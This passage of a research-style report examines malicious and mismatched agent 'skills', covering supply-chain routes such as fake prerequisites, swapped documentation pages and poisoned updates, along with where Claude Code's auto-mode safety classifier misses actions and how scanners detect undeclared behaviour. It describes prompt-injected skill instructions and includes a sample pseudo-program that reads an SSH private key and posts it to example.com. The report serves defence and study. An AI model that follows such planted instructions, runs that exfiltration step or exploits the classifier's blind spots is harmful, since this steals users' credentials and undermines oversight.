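Claude Code's auto mode immediately allows read-only tools, actions covered by the user's narrower rules and edits inside the project folder. The classifier, a model that stands in for the user, reviews everything else, including shell commands and web requests. It first makes a quick yes-or-no judgement that leans towards blocking, then reasons at length only about the actions it flagged. If it still blocks an action, Claude receives the reason and tries another approach. After three blocks in a row, or twenty in a session, Claude Code goes back to asking the user.

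Anthropic measured the classifier's errors on three sets of actions. The classifier wrongly blocked 0.4% of 10,000 ordinary actions from employees' sessions. It missed 5.7% of 1,000 synthetic attempts to send data out, and 17% (about nine) of 52 real actions in which Claude had overstepped what a user wanted. The last set is the most realistic but very small.

In most of the misses that Anthropic examined, the classifier identified the action as dangerous but wrongly treated it as authorised by the user. In one case, a user asked Claude to "clean up" a proposed code change, and the classifier took this as permission to overwrite the project's history. Anthropic tried rewording the classifier's instructions, but each change did more harm than good. The company wrote that auto mode was no substitute for careful human review of high-stakes systems.

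Later results for auto mode look better. In the experiment with 1,053 testers, auto mode blocked 89% of the dangerous commands, and the testers blocked 13.6%. It stopped 800 commands that a tester had approved, while testers stopped six that it had allowed. Apollo Research, which tests AI systems for safety, built attacks that auto mode missed 12% of the time before Anthropic strengthened it and 7% afterwards. Anthropic also examined real sessions that its safety systems had flagged. It found serious harm that the user had not explicitly asked for in 2.4% of those run in auto mode and 6.3% of those with manual approval. That comparison is less convincing, because users chose their own mode and may have used the two for different work.

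The evidence favours auto mode over an inattentive user. There is less evidence on how it compares with a reviewer who reads each request, or how it handles a limit that only the user knows. Li, Khabra and colleagues replayed 50 real work sessions and marked 291 points where the agent went beyond what the user had authorised. ConLeash flagged 278 of them and auto mode stopped six. The researchers used ConLeash's definition of a boundary, which gave ConLeash a large advantage, and they acknowledge that auto mode has a different purpose. Auto mode checks whether an action looks dangerous in itself, so it let the agent delete a folder in one project when the user had permitted work only in another.

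In the design Anthropic describes, the classifier receives the user's messages and the agent's commands, but not Claude's own prose or the output of tools. For a script bundled with a skill, such as `extract.py`, it therefore seems to get only a line naming the file, even when Claude has read the source. One of the default rules blocks code copied from outside repositories, which may stop some skill scripts, but none of these tests has separate results for skills. At launch, Anthropic's *Auto mode for Claude Code* still recommended using the feature in isolated environments.

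### What can be inferred about installation

The figures on fatigue do not apply directly to installing skills. Someone who installs one skill a month is not answering dozens of installation prompts a day, and may well read the description carefully.

Wu and colleagues' results are more relevant, because their participants had time, a warning and a specific task, and still misjudged which data the task needed. Someone installing a skill has a harder judgment to make, because they must decide which data it will need for tasks they haven't thought of yet, usually without a list of the data involved. They would probably do no better than Wu's participants.

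Like people installing a skill, Yan's participants had to decide about future actions, and they mostly postponed the decision. Some people may likewise install a skill assuming they will get to approve anything important later. That assumption would be reasonable for the agent's own commands in Claude Code's Manual mode, but much less so in auto mode or for whatever a script does once it has started.

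The closest direct precedent is Android's old practice of asking people to accept an app's permissions when they installed it. Yan cites a 2012 study of Android users for the finding that people may overlook or misunderstand permissions. Wu and colleagues note that phones have since largely moved to asking when an app needs access. Those Android users were shown a list of permissions, which a skill's description doesn't provide, so their behaviour is only a rough guide to what people do with the description.

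A direct test would be fairly easy to run. Researchers could let people choose skills from a marketplace page, ask them which actions they believed they had approved, and compare their answers with what each skill could do.

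## How undisclosed behaviour enters a skill

To run such a test, researchers would first need to know what each skill can do, and its folder doesn't hold the whole answer. Part of a skill's behaviour may come from programs and web pages that other people control, and part may arrive months after installation. There are six main entry points:

| Entry point | Who controls the content | When it arrives | What an inspection at installation can see |
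|---|---|---|---|
| Bundled script | The skill's author | With the folder | All of the code |
| Instruction body | The skill's author | With the folder | All of the text, but not how a model will act on it |
| Claimed prerequisite | Whoever hosts the download | Before first use | The request, but often not the program |
| Software dependency | The dependency's publisher | When the script runs | The name, but not later versions |
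| External page | The website's owner | When the agent reads it | The address, but not later content |
| Update | Whoever controls the skill's source | Any time after installation | Nothing |

### Bundled scripts

Suppose the developer of `pdf-text` adds a line to `extract.py` that sends a copy of every invoice to a server. The line is in the folder from the first day, so anyone who reads Python can find it, just as a programmer could have found the function that Cato added to Anthropic's GIF skill.

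Real attackers have done much the same. In early 2026 the security company Koi (2026) audited all 2,857 skills on ClawHub, a marketplace for users of OpenClaw. Two of them offered to search Polymarket, a site where people bet on future events, and contained what looked like working search code. That code also fetched a program from the attacker's server and ran it, which gave the attacker live control of the user's computer. Another skill, rankaj, posed as a weather tool and sent the file with the runtime's access keys to an outside address. According to *ClawHavoc*, a report from the Chinese antivirus company Antiy CERT, rankaj did retrieve weather data from a genuine public service.

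People who get the forecast they asked for have little reason to look at the code. Koi thinks whoever wrote the Polymarket skills also counted on hurried reviewers, who tend to check the installation steps and skim the rest.

Some malicious skills reuse older code. In *Do Not Mention This to the User*, Liu, Chen and colleagues (2026) found a calculator skill whose script gave an attacker remote control of the computer. In *MalSkillBench*, Guo, Jia and colleagues (2026) matched that script to a malicious Python package whose code was identical except for the attacker's address. Defenders who already collect malicious packages can therefore recognise some malicious skill scripts.

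### The instruction body

Reviewers can read `SKILL.md` without knowing Python, so a harmful instruction there should be easier to spot than harmful code. But they have to open the raw file. Liu and colleagues describe skills with instructions in comments or invisible characters, which a formatted view leaves out.

The short description needs the same scrutiny. SafeDep's *Agent Skills Threat Model* points out that the runtime always loads this field, so an instruction hidden there reaches the model even in sessions that never use the skill.

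The security company Zenity (2026) reported two skills that used instructions to protect or spread themselves. One told the agent to change its own system prompt so that the agent would reinstall the skill if anyone deleted it. The other replaced Anthropic's skill for writing new skills without telling the user. Neither needs a bundled program, because the agent already has the necessary access.

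Attacks through text are less reliable than attacks through code. To build a test set, Guo and colleagues generated malicious skills automatically and ran each one with a real coding agent in a sandbox. The attack worked as intended in 94.5% of the samples where the harmful part was code and 75.8% of those where it was text. A script runs the same way each time, while a model may ignore or refuse an instruction. This may be one reason why Guo and colleagues found hardly any text attacks among the malicious skills they collected from public sites.

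### Claimed prerequisites and ClawHavoc

Many honest skills need other software, so users aren't surprised to be told to install something first. The campaign that Koi named ClawHavoc exploited this. Its skills posed as cryptocurrency wallet trackers, YouTube summarisers, automatic updaters and connectors for Google's office programs. Antiy found that they came with 500 to 700 lines of documentation, which a language model had probably written. A prerequisites section claimed that the skill would not work without a helper program.

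On Windows, the "helper" was a trojan that records keystrokes. On a Mac, the documentation included a command to paste into the terminal. The command installed Atomic Stealer, which criminals can rent for $500 to $1,000 a month. This program copies saved passwords, browser data, login keys and the contents of more than 60 kinds of cryptocurrency wallet.

The attackers kept these programs on other sites, so a scan of the skill's folder could have found the request, which was visible in `SKILL.md`, but not the programs themselves. They also protected the Windows download with a password, which kept antivirus software from scanning its contents. A free helper tool has no obvious need for a password, so this could have alerted a suspicious reader.

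It is less clear whether the user or the agent was supposed to follow these steps. Koi and Antiy mostly describe a user who downloads the file or pastes the command. Guo and colleagues describe an agent that reads the prerequisite and installs it. If the agent follows the steps, the runtime can at least ask for approval or run the download in a sandbox. If the user follows them by hand, the malware starts outside the runtime, where limits on the agent or the skill's scripts would not stop it.

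The published counts of ClawHavoc skills look inconsistent. Koi's first audit found 341 malicious skills among the 2,857 on ClawHub and attributed 335 of them to the campaign. Antiy reported 1,184 as of 5 February 2026, four days after Koi's disclosure.

Most of the gap seems to come from what each company counted. Koi's audit covered the skills listed on ClawHub at the time. Antiy went through ClawHub's historical repository and included packages that had since been taken down. The attackers were also uploading quickly. Antiy says the mass uploads began on 31 January, when seven accounts published 386 malicious skills, and Koi disclosed the campaign the next day. Antiy's total also includes rankaj and the Polymarket skills, which Koi listed separately from ClawHavoc. Two accounts uploaded 1,067 of Antiy's 1,184 packages.

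Neither number gives a lasting rate for ClawHub. The 1,184 malicious packages can't be divided by the 3,498 skills that Antiy says remained on the site when it published, because ClawHub had already removed most of those packages. Koi kept scanning, and by 16 February it had found 824 malicious skills in a marketplace that had grown past 10,700. The number of known malicious skills had more than doubled, but their share had fallen from about 12% to under 8%.

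Both companies sell security products, and Koi used its report to introduce a scanner. But the campaign's existence is well established. OpenSourceMalware, a site that tracks malicious packages, described it separately and traced it to the same control server.

Nobody seems to know how many people it harmed. Sixty packages from one uploader were still available when Antiy published, and together they had been downloaded 14,285 times. A download doesn't show that anyone installed the fake helper.

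Fake prerequisites also appeared in 607 (86%) of the 703 malicious skills that Guo and colleagues gathered from public registries and sharing platforms. But 81% of the 703 came from two accounts, and Guo and colleagues attribute most of the sample to a single cryptocurrency-theft campaign. The 86% figure therefore mainly describes how one group of attackers worked in early 2026, and doesn't show that most attackers prefer this method or that the next campaign will use it. Guo and colleagues make a similar point about detection tools, reporting that one tool's detection rate differed by 66 percentage points depending on whether they tested it only on this sample or on their wider set.

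### Software dependencies

A script usually relies on libraries that other people wrote. For example, `extract.py` needs one that can read PDF files. The script's author can specify an exact version of the library or just its name, in which case the installer usually fetches the newest version.

SafeDep, a company that checks open-source software, made a sample skill that formats code. Its script depends on a harmless library but doesn't specify a fixed version. When the agent runs the script, a standard Python tool downloads the library's latest release and starts the program, with no separate installation step. No malicious code exists when the skill is reviewed. If the library's publisher later releases a harmful version, later runs of the skill can download it, even though nobody has edited the skill.

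SafeDep did not publish a harmful version, so it demonstrated the mechanism without harming anyone. It doesn't blame the Python tool, because authors can pin the version, though many don't. A reviewer could have noticed that the script named the library without a version number and rejected the skill for that. But reading the script more closely would not have revealed what a later version of the library would do.

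The publisher of a package that a skill uses may be the skill's author under another name, or a stranger who has never heard of the skill. SafeDep warns that a skill may also refer to a package that doesn't exist, often because a language model made up the name, and that an attacker can then register it. Zenity found signs that attackers prepare for this kind of confusion. Starting from one skill with instructions to install an unverified Python package, its researchers found hundreds of look-alike package names that somebody had reserved and left empty.

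### External pages

Some skills have the agent read a web page, such as a product's current manual. This keeps the skill up to date, but it also lets the page's owner give the agent new instructions at any time.

In June 2026 the security company AIR tried this on the public. It wrote a skill called brand-landingpage and described it as interviewing users about their brand and building them a web page with Stitch, Google's design tool. According to The Hacker News (2026), AIR submitted the skill to a marketplace repository with 156 skills and about 36,000 stars, GitHub's equivalent of likes. The marketplace accepted it after a few days, so it appeared under a popular name. AIR then ran an Instagram advertisement aimed at marketers, salespeople and designers.

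The skill contained no malicious code. In *Anatomy of a Malicious AI Skill*, Hoppe (2026) found that the file's setup steps instructed the agent to follow Stitch's online documentation, install the software if it was missing and spare the user the technical details. Hoppe says an honest author might write the same steps for a new product. But AIR owned the address given for the documentation. At first it led to Google's real documentation, and every skill scanner that AIR tried approved the skill. Once enough people had installed it, AIR replaced the page with instructions to download and run a script. The script sent the user's email address to AIR and did nothing else.

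AIR used these messages to count the agents it had reached, and reported about 26,000, including some on corporate accounts. The Hacker News stresses that nobody has independently confirmed this figure and that AIR was launching its own skill marketplace. The rest of the account is easier to check, since Hoppe found the submission and its review on GitHub, and the file was still online in September.

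Hoppe thinks that nobody could have noticed the substitution without already knowing the address of Google's tool. That seems too pessimistic, because a reviewer could have looked up who owned the site. The reviewer still could not have known what the page would contain later. This is true even of a page with an honest owner, because the owner may sell the site or lose control of it.

### Updates

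After a user approves a skill, an update can change any of its files. Whoever controls the skill's source decides what the update contains. This is usually the original author, but it may be someone who has taken over the author's account.

The largest reported case became public in August 2026. Attackers had copied skills for two popular AI tools, Paperclip and Browser Use, and published them under similar names on skills.sh, a registry run by the cloud company Vercel. According to Zenity Labs' *Attackers Target Agents via The Skill Supply Chain*, the Paperclip copies were clean at first and gathered installations. On 11 July the attackers added code that fetched a second program, which collected login credentials. The skills were popular on the registry throughout the month. A reviewer who inspected one of the Paperclip copies in early July would have found a working skill with a slightly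 wrong name and no malicious code.

By 2 August, skills.sh showed more than 1.7 million installations across the family. Zenity reported this total from the registry's own counters, which don't count unique users, so someone who installs several of the skills, or one skill on several machines, presumably appears more than once. The total also includes installations from before 11 July, when no harmful version was available. The Next Web's *Malicious AI ‘skills’ turned agents into credential thieves, at scale* repeats Zenity's warning that these are not unique victims. TechRadar's headline, *Experts warn malicious AI skills are hitting more victims than ever*, is less careful. There appears to be no independent count of the people who installed the malicious version or of those who lost credentials.

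Vercel and Microsoft have removed the malicious skills, but TechRadar notes that users must delete installed copies themselves. Zenity also reported a skill that reached more than 250,000 installations over several months and entered a major registry's top 150 before anyone flagged it. The installation figure comes from Zenity's announcement of a scanning service it was launching, and it probably has the same weakness as the larger figure.

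Attackers can also take over a skill's source without breaking into an account. Many marketplaces only list skills and leave the files on GitHub. If an author renames their GitHub account, someone else can claim the old name and publish different files at the address the marketplace still links to. This works even if the original skill contains nothing suspicious. The security feed CraftedSignal cites a study of 238,180 skills, 121 of which pointed to seven repositories open to this kind of takeover. The most popular of these skills had just over 2,000 downloads, so the known exposure is small.

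### How many skills are malicious

Estimates of how many published skills are malicious differ by a factor of more than 70. Liu and colleagues probably did the most careful count, and theirs is also the lowest. In January 2026 they collected 98,380 skills from two registries, skills.rest and skillsmp, and narrowed them down in three steps:

1. They searched the scripts and instructions for 14 suspicious patterns, such as reading access keys, and had a language model examine the instructions. This left 4,287 skills.
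2. They ran each of these in an isolated container with fake credentials as bait, and recorded its files, network connections and system calls. In 762 cases they saw something suspicious, such as a connection to a site that the documentation didn't mention.
3. Two of the researchers independently reviewed the 762, compared what each skill did with what it claimed to do, and confirmed 157 as malicious.

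The 157 skills make up 0.16% of the total. The registries removed all of them after the researchers reported them. Liu and colleagues take the removals as independent support for their judgement, though a registry has little reason to defend a skill that security researchers have reported.

The method misses some malicious skills. The researchers did not run the 94,093 skills that matched no pattern, and they ran the others for at most 60 seconds at a time, so those may not have shown everything they could do. A skill like AIR's would have passed as long as its external page was harmless. The study also left out private skills, vendors' official collections and skills that were dangerous only through carelessness. As in Guo's sample, one attacker skews the results, because 54.1% of the malicious skills came from a single source that imitated well-known brands.

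Other researchers studied different marketplaces and used different standards of proof. The table includes the security company Snyk's *Exploring the Threat Landscape of Agent Skills*, the ClawHub audit *ClawdPwned*, and a count by the antivirus company ESET, reported in Expert Insights' *Thousands Of Malicious Skills Are Hiding In AI Agent Marketplaces, ESET Warns* (2026).

| Count | Where | Skills examined | Malicious | Share |
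|---|---|---:|---:|---:|
| Koi, first audit | ClawHub | 2,857 | 341 | 11.9% |
| *ClawdPwned* | ClawHub | 2,556 | 49 ("likely") | 1.9% |
| Snyk | ClawHub and skills.sh | 3,984 | 76 | 1.9% |
| ESET | AI agent marketplaces | about 900,000 | over 3,000 | about 0.3% |
| Liu and colleagues | skills.rest and skillsmp | 98,380 | 157 | 0.16% |

ClawHub's high share in Koi's audit reflects the audit's timing as much as the marketplace itself. Koi did the audit while ClawHavoc was under way, and a few accounts can upload hundreds of nearly identical skills in a day. The antivirus company Bitdefender estimated an even higher share, about 17% of the OpenClaw skills it analysed from the platform's first weeks, according to Unit 42, the research group of the security company Palo Alto Networks. The registries that Liu and colleagues studied, by contrast, mainly index skills that are already on GitHub.

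These percentages do not give a user's chance of installing a malicious skill, because most listings probably have few users, while a popular malicious skill can have hundreds of thousands of installations. Automated scanners flag a much larger share of skills, up to 46.8% of one marketplace according to *Malicious Or Not* (Holzbauer, Schmidt and colleagues, 2026), but these warnings are not confirmed cases.

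### Excess behaviour without an attacker

Liu and colleagues classified a skill as malicious only if its code or instructions pointed to deliberate abuse. They did not confirm malice in the other 605 skills flagged in the containers. Some of those were presumably false alarms, but a skill can also contact an undocumented site because its author forgot to mention it.

Careless authors can expose users too. They might send documents to services the user would not have chosen, leave a library's version unpinned, or link to a manual on a site that later changes hands. In any of these cases, the user's invoice can end up on a stranger's server.

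Snyk's figures suggest that flaws are much more common than malice. Of 3,984 skills, it found at least one critical security problem in 534 and confirmed malicious code in 76. Simple mismatches are even more common, and Unit 42 reports that declared and actual behaviour differ in 80% of 49,943 OpenClaw skills. CraftedSignal mentions skills published with working access keys for online services. Such a mistake harms the author first, because strangers can run up their bill. But a skill that uses its author's key presumably also sends the user's requests through the author's account, which few descriptions would mention.

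The agent can also take steps that nobody wrote into the skill. Suppose the invoice is a scanned image, `extract.py` returns no text, and `SKILL.md` doesn't cover this case. To finish the summary, the agent might install a text-recognition program or upload the invoice to a free online service. A reviewer could read every file in the folder without finding that step. If the model also gets the program's name wrong, it may install whatever somebody has registered under the wrong name, which is the risk SafeDep describes.

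There seem to be no figures on how often agents improvise like this while following a skill. They do overstep in ordinary work, since the 52 actions Anthropic used to test auto mode were real cases of Claude going beyond a user's wishes. Skills may reduce the problem by giving the agent a tested procedure, which leaves it less to make up. They may also make it worse if the author tells the agent to solve problems without bothering the user. AIR relied on such an instruction, which would leave the same decisions to the agent in an honest skill.

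## Comparing a skill's description with its code before installation

Inspecting a skill's folder cannot predict the steps an agent will improvise later, but software can compare the files in the folder with one another before anyone installs the skill. Researchers published several tools for this in 2026. They address three different questions, which `extract.py` can illustrate:

- **Is the skill malicious?** It is if the author wrote the script to steal invoices.
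- **Is it vulnerable?** It is if an honest author pasted the PDF's file name straight into a shell command, so that a PDF with a specially written name could run a command of an attacker's choice.
- **Does the code exceed the description?** It does if the script sends scanned pages to an online text-recognition service and the description never mentions one.

A skill can have any one of these problems without the others. For example, about a third of the listings in which Pandey and colleagues found any sign of a threat were offensive security tools. A password cracker may be dangerous even if its description accurately says that it cracks passwords.

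ClawHub scans skills with VirusTotal, a service that combines the verdicts of many antivirus products. *ClawHub Security Signals* (Koc and colleagues, 2026) compared VirusTotal and two other scanners on 67,453 skill versions. According to Pandey and colleagues, the paper also observed that a skill with harmless content can still be risky if it grants too much authority.

*Agent Skills in the Wild* (Liu, Wang and colleagues, 2026) is the usual source for the claim that 26.1% of skills are vulnerable. The researchers collected 42,447 skills but analysed only 31,132, so the figure represents roughly 8,100 skills. They looked for patterns in the files that resemble known flaws. A match is a reason to look more closely, but it doesn't prove that an attacker could exploit the skill.

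Neither result tells a user whether the code keeps to its description.

### How SkillScope (He et al.) finds a mismatch

He, Li and colleagues (2026), in *Do Skill Descriptions Tell the Truth?*, built a tool called SkillScope for the third question. They use "description" to mean the whole of `SKILL.md`, including the instructions to the agent. Wu et al.'s SkillScope is an unrelated tool that checks permissions while a skill runs.

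To decide which behaviour matters for security, two of the researchers first read the `SKILL.md` files of 920 skills and sorted the actions they declared into 11 categories: reading files, writing files, running commands, accessing the network, calling external services, accessing secrets, changing installed software, using system permissions, applying security controls, logging, and exposing health checks. SkillScope then examines each skill in three steps.

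1. **Find the operations.** Keyword rules search the code for calls in these categories, such as `os.getenv(` for secrets or `requests.post(` for the network. Each match becomes a point in a graph. Each point keeps the matching code instead of the name of its category, because reading a private key and reading an ordinary data file are both "reading files".
2. **Connect them.** The tool links two points if data or control can pass from one to the other, even through several ordinary steps in between. It also follows connections from one file to another. For one PDF skill with eight code files, the graph had 250 points and 301 links.
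3. **Compare the graph with the text.** A language model, GPT-5, receives `SKILL.md`, the graph and the list of categories. It notes what `SKILL.md` declares and then checks every point and link against that.

The model reports a mismatch if the code uses something that no declared function mentions or implies, such as a credential or an outside service. It also reports one if data crosses a security boundary along a path that `SKILL.md` doesn't cover, for instance from a local secret to an outside server.

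He and colleagues give the example of a skill described only as "Read target files and run a fixed analysis workflow." Its code calls `os.getenv('API_KEY')`, which reads an access key from the computer's settings, and then `requests.post(endpoint, headers={...})`, which sends a request to a server. Step 1 finds both calls, and step 2 links them because the request includes the key. In step 3, the model finds no mention of either call's action in the description. The skill has an undeclared behaviour (reading the key) and an undeclared flow (sending a local secret to an outside address).

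Code that only adds detail to the description doesn't count as a mismatch. If `SKILL.md` lists a summary report as the skill's output and the script saves that report as `output/report.json`, the description is less specific than the code but still covers what the code does.

### How many of the alarms are right

He et al. ran SkillScope on 4,556 skills with code in Python, JavaScript, TypeScript or Go, collected from Anthropic, OpenAI and two marketplaces. Two of them also reviewed every skill by hand, without seeing each other's answers or the tool's. They confirmed mismatches in 428 skills (9.4%) and judged another 1,106 descriptions (24.3%) to be merely less detailed than the code.

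SkillScope flagged 487 skills, of which 413 had a real mismatch and 74 did not. It missed 15 real mismatches. Its precision, the share of alarms that were right, was 84.8%, and its recall, the share of real mismatches that it found, was 96.5%. A marketplace that checked 1,000 similar skills could expect about 107 alarms, a manageable number for human reviewers. About 91 of these would be correct and 16 false, and about three mismatches would be missed.

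Most of the false alarms came from treating extra detail as a mismatch. Fourteen of the 15 misses came from the keyword rules, which search for common calls like `requests.post(` and can miss the same action when the code uses an online service's own library.

To see which parts of the tool mattered, He and colleagues removed them one at a time on a random sample of 300 skills, 38 of which had a mismatch:

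| Version | Correct alarms | False alarms | Missed |
|---|---:|---:|---:|
| Full tool | 36 | 5 | 2 |
| Without the categories | 34 | 13 | 4 |
| Without the graph (model reads raw code) | 30 | 3 | 8 |
| Without either | 31 | 16 | 7 |

The model flagged many harmless details as mismatches without the list of categories. It missed more real mismatches when the graph was removed, mostly where data flows between distant parts of the code. Both effects are plausible, but with only 38 mismatches, each count is small.

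The human review deserves some caution because each reviewer got through all 4,556 skills in about nine working days, or roughly one a minute, using the same criteria and categories as the tool. The accuracy figures therefore measure how well SkillScope agrees with a quick human reading under its own rules. The reviewers agreed with the tool on all 1,106 less detailed descriptions, which is surprising for such a fine judgement.

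The 9.4% is not a rate of deception either. In 212 of the 413 mismatches that SkillScope caught, the code sent a credential to an outside service without this being fully disclosed. Sometimes `SKILL.md` did describe the service and left out only the credential. Many online services require a key with every request, so many of these cases are probably ordinary code with an incomplete description.

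In another respect the figure is too low, because He and colleagues count everything in `SKILL.md` as declared, and a user who reads only the short description field never sees most of that file. If a line near the end tells the agent to upload the invoice, they count the upload as declared even if it would surprise the user.

### Why other studies find far more mismatches

Other researchers report much higher rates, mainly because they count different things. *SkillConsist* (Meng, Zheng and colleagues, 2026) covers undeclared behaviour, described features that the code lacks, and direct conflicts between the description and the code. *Why Static Skill Inconsistencies Do Not Equate to Runtime Risks* (Fan, Wang and colleagues, 2026) counts contradictions anywhere in a skill, even between two sentences of its documentation. One example is a charting skill that names version 6 of a library in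 one place and version 7.9.0 in another.

| Source | Skills | What counts as a mismatch | Share affected |
|---|---|---|---:|
| He and colleagues | 4,556 with code | Code goes beyond `SKILL.md` | 9.4% |
| Meng and colleagues | ClawHub's 500 most downloaded | Undeclared, missing or conflicting behaviour | 52% |
| Pandey and colleagues | 770 that pre-approve tools | The tool list understates what the files can do | 59% |
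| Fan and colleagues | 575 from GitHub and a benchmark | Contradictions among documents, code and environment | 67% |
| Unit 42 | 49,943 for OpenClaw | Declared and actual behaviour differ | 80% |

The first row is the most relevant to someone deciding whether to install a skill, because only code that goes beyond the description widens the consent gap. Most of the faults in the second and fourth rows are promises that no code implements, or contradictions between the description and the code. Of the 442 faults that Meng and colleagues recorded across their whole test set, 218 were unimplemented promises, 183 were contradictions and only 41 were undeclared behaviour.

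Their tool, SkillConsist, searches in both directions. A language model first breaks the whole folder into short records, each giving a condition, the thing affected, the effect and the location in the files. It sorts these records by role, regardless of file type. A sentence in `SKILL.md` that tells the agent to run a script and upload the result counts as implementation, because the agent will carry it out. A sample command that shows users the available options counts as a declaration.

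SkillConsist then builds one graph of the skill's declarations and another of its implementation. To check a declared feature, such as exporting a table, it searches the implementation graph for a connected series of steps that implement the feature. To check an action in the code, such as an upload, it searches the declaration graph for text that covers the action. One sentence can match many steps, which helps because descriptions are nearly always shorter than the code.

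The tool reports something as missing only after searching everywhere it could be. When Meng and colleagues switched this rule off, reported faults rose from 858 to 5,792, and 5,039 of those were false. Finding a conflict between two passages is evidently much easier than establishing that nothing in a folder mentions an upload.

The researchers tested SkillConsist on 633 skills: the 500 from ClawHub and 133 from a collection built to study attacks through skill files. Two reviewers found faults in 319 of them. SkillConsist correctly flagged 284 of these and wrongly flagged 43 of the other 314, for a precision of 86.85% and a recall of 89.03%. It was worse at locating the faults, finding only 257 of the 442. A flag from SkillConsist is therefore a fair reason to inspect a skill, but the reviewer may have to find the fault independently.

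Meng and colleagues also ran an adapted version of He and colleagues' SkillScope on the same skills, and it found only seven of the 319. The broader definition explains most of the misses, since SkillScope doesn't look for broken promises. But it also found none of the 41 undeclared behaviours. Some of those may be in the prose of `SKILL.md`, which SkillScope treats as part of the description. The adapted version may also perform worse than the original, as can happen when researchers adapt a competing tool. Even so, the result is a reason to doubt that SkillScope would catch 96.5% of mismatches outside its own dataset.

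### When the instructions and the code do harm together

In some skills, neither the instructions nor the code looks wrong until someone reads them together. Zhao, Wang and colleagues (2026), in *From Instructions to Exploits*, describe one called pptx_skill, which edits PowerPoint files. After the editing steps, `SKILL.md` requires the agent to always run a backup script on the finished presentation. The script uploads whatever file it receives to a stranger's server. The instruction looks like a routine precaution, and many legitimate scripts upload files, but following this instruction sends the user's own document to the stranger.

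Zhao and colleagues' scanner handles this by translating the prose into something like a program. A language model turns each instruction into calls from a short fixed list. For "read the login key and upload it to example.com", the result would look roughly like this:

```
v0 = read_file("~/.ssh/id_rsa")
http_post("https://example.com", v0)
```

The scanner joins this program to a graph of the bundled scripts, so it can follow a file from an instruction into a script and out to the network. It labels each piece of data by how trustworthy its source is, how sensitive it is and which operations produced it. It then applies fixed rules to find dangerous combinations, such as sensitive data reaching a network call. A language model translates the instructions, and it translated 92.5% to 94.5% of 400 sampled instructions correctly, depending on the model used. It decides whether a skill is dangerous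 only in a few ambiguous cases.

The scanner looks for malicious skills but doesn't compare their code with their descriptions. Averaged over five language models, it caught about 111 of 117 malicious skills and wrongly flagged about 28 of 117 harmless ones, for a precision of 80.2% and a recall of 95.2%. It also caught pptx_skill, a malicious skill that the rule-based scanner SkillFortify passed as harmless.

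When Zhao and colleagues scanned 66,157 ClawHub skills collected on 20 April 2026, the tool flagged 2,473. The researchers ran these in a test environment, reviewed them by hand, and confirmed 627 as malicious. That is about one in four, compared with four in five in the balanced test, where half the skills were malicious. Some of the others may have been malicious without leaving enough evidence to confirm it, but the share was probably lower mainly because only about 1% of the skills in the marketplace were malicious.

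Two accounts published 88% of the 627 skills. By 15 July, only 23 of them were still identifiable in ClawHub's registry. A marketplace can remove many malicious skills by acting against a few accounts, at least while attackers upload in bulk.

Mismatches between a skill's description and its code can also help find malicious skills. Meng and colleagues added SkillConsist's findings to an existing two-stage check, in which a scan of the files selects skills for a test run. With 13 more test runs, the check caught 53 of 84 malicious skills, up from 42, but it still missed more than a third of them.

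### Listing what a skill could do

Pandey and colleagues suggest that marketplaces could show a profile of what each skill's files could make the agent do, with evidence for each item. They score signs of malice separately, so the profile does not depend on the author's intentions. It also avoids the problem of interpreting the description, because it can list a script's file uploads whether or not the author mentioned them.

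They illustrate this with an imaginary skill that uploads reports. Its script reads a report, takes an access token from the computer's settings and sends the report to an online service. The profile would list shell commands, file reading, credential use and network access. The reviewer would then know to check how sensitive the report is, what the token permits and whether the destination is authorised. A company might still refuse the skill, even though nothing in it is malicious and its description may be accurate.

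Pandey and colleagues scanned 6,309 listings and placed 1,621 in the two highest levels of exposure. Of those, 1,306 showed no sign of malice strong enough to flag, so a malware scan would let nearly all of them through. The researchers also read 140 randomly chosen listings that their scanner had rated harmless and found no missed threats. This suggests that most of the highly exposed skills are benign but have broad access.

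Searching for combinations of capabilities narrows the list. Only 397 listings could both use credentials and send data over the network. In 628, the skill had access to private data, exposure to untrusted content and a way to send data out, which together make data theft possible. People could read a few hundred skills by hand, and Pandey and colleagues propose that marketplaces start with these.

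The profiles have their own weaknesses. Metano Labs, where three of the researchers work, built and operates the scanner, which uses a language model to infer the profiles from the files. Pandey and colleagues acknowledge that no third party has evaluated it. When they rescanned 89 listings, the verdict on whether a listing was malicious stayed the same for only 84% of them. A profile can also include abilities that a skill doesn't use in a given session. Half the listings seemed able to run shell commands, but only about one in twelve did so during a test session.

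It is also unclear how much a profile would help an ordinary user. A shell can do almost anything the user's account can, so "can run shell commands" is the most serious item in a profile, but it appears on about half of all skills. Users may learn to ignore it, as they learn to ignore permission prompts. Pandey and colleagues have not tested profiles on users, and they say that someone should.

### What happened when inconsistent skills ran

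A mismatch in a skill's files may never affect anyone, because the faulty script may not run or the agent may notice the problem and work around it. Fan and colleagues tested this after they audited 575 skills and found 1,182 confirmed inconsistencies.

They built 49 tasks, each designed to lead the agent to one real inconsistency. Three models, Claude Haiku 4.5, Qwen3.6-35B and DeepSeek-V4-Flash, attempted every task three times with the original skill and three times with a minimally repaired copy. A program then checked the results. This produced 441 pairs of runs:

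| What happened with the original skill | Pairs |
|---|---:|
| The agent followed the fault and failed a check that it passed with the repaired skill | 97 |
| The agent ran into the fault but still passed | 155 |
| The agent failed the check with both versions | 103 |
| The fault had no effect, or the agent avoided it or never read the skill | 86 |

The researchers designed the tasks to trigger the inconsistency, yet it clearly spoiled the result in only 22% of the pairs. The share would probably be lower in ordinary use. The effect varied greatly by model. Haiku followed the faulty skill and failed in 44 of its 147 pairs, while DeepSeek did so in only 18, although both read the skill nearly every time. Repairing the skill raised Haiku's average score from 0.741 to 0.877 but DeepSeek's only from 0.870 to 0.893.

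Fan and colleagues conclude that the number of inconsistencies in a skill is a poor measure of its risk in use. Their evidence supports this for reliability risks. A documented function that doesn't exist causes a problem only if a task needs it, and even then a good model can often write a replacement.

The result doesn't apply to undeclared access. Fan and colleagues' audit tool leaves out cases where the code does more than the documentation describes, which they consider usually harmless. Only two of the 1,182 findings were of that kind, so the experiment tested almost no cases like He and colleagues' undeclared key. An agent can react to a missing documented function because it gets an error or a wrong result, but even a strong model gets no such signal when `extract.py` quietly sends the invoice elsewhere.

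A security reviewer should care about code that no task reaches, even though it does not harm reliability. Pandey and colleagues found a family of listings with a setup script that makes lasting changes to the agent's configuration. No file in these skills refers to the script, so it never ran in their tests. It would run if an agent tried it while looking for a way to fix a problem, or if a later version of `SKILL.md` included an instruction to run it.

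### Vague descriptions and missing code

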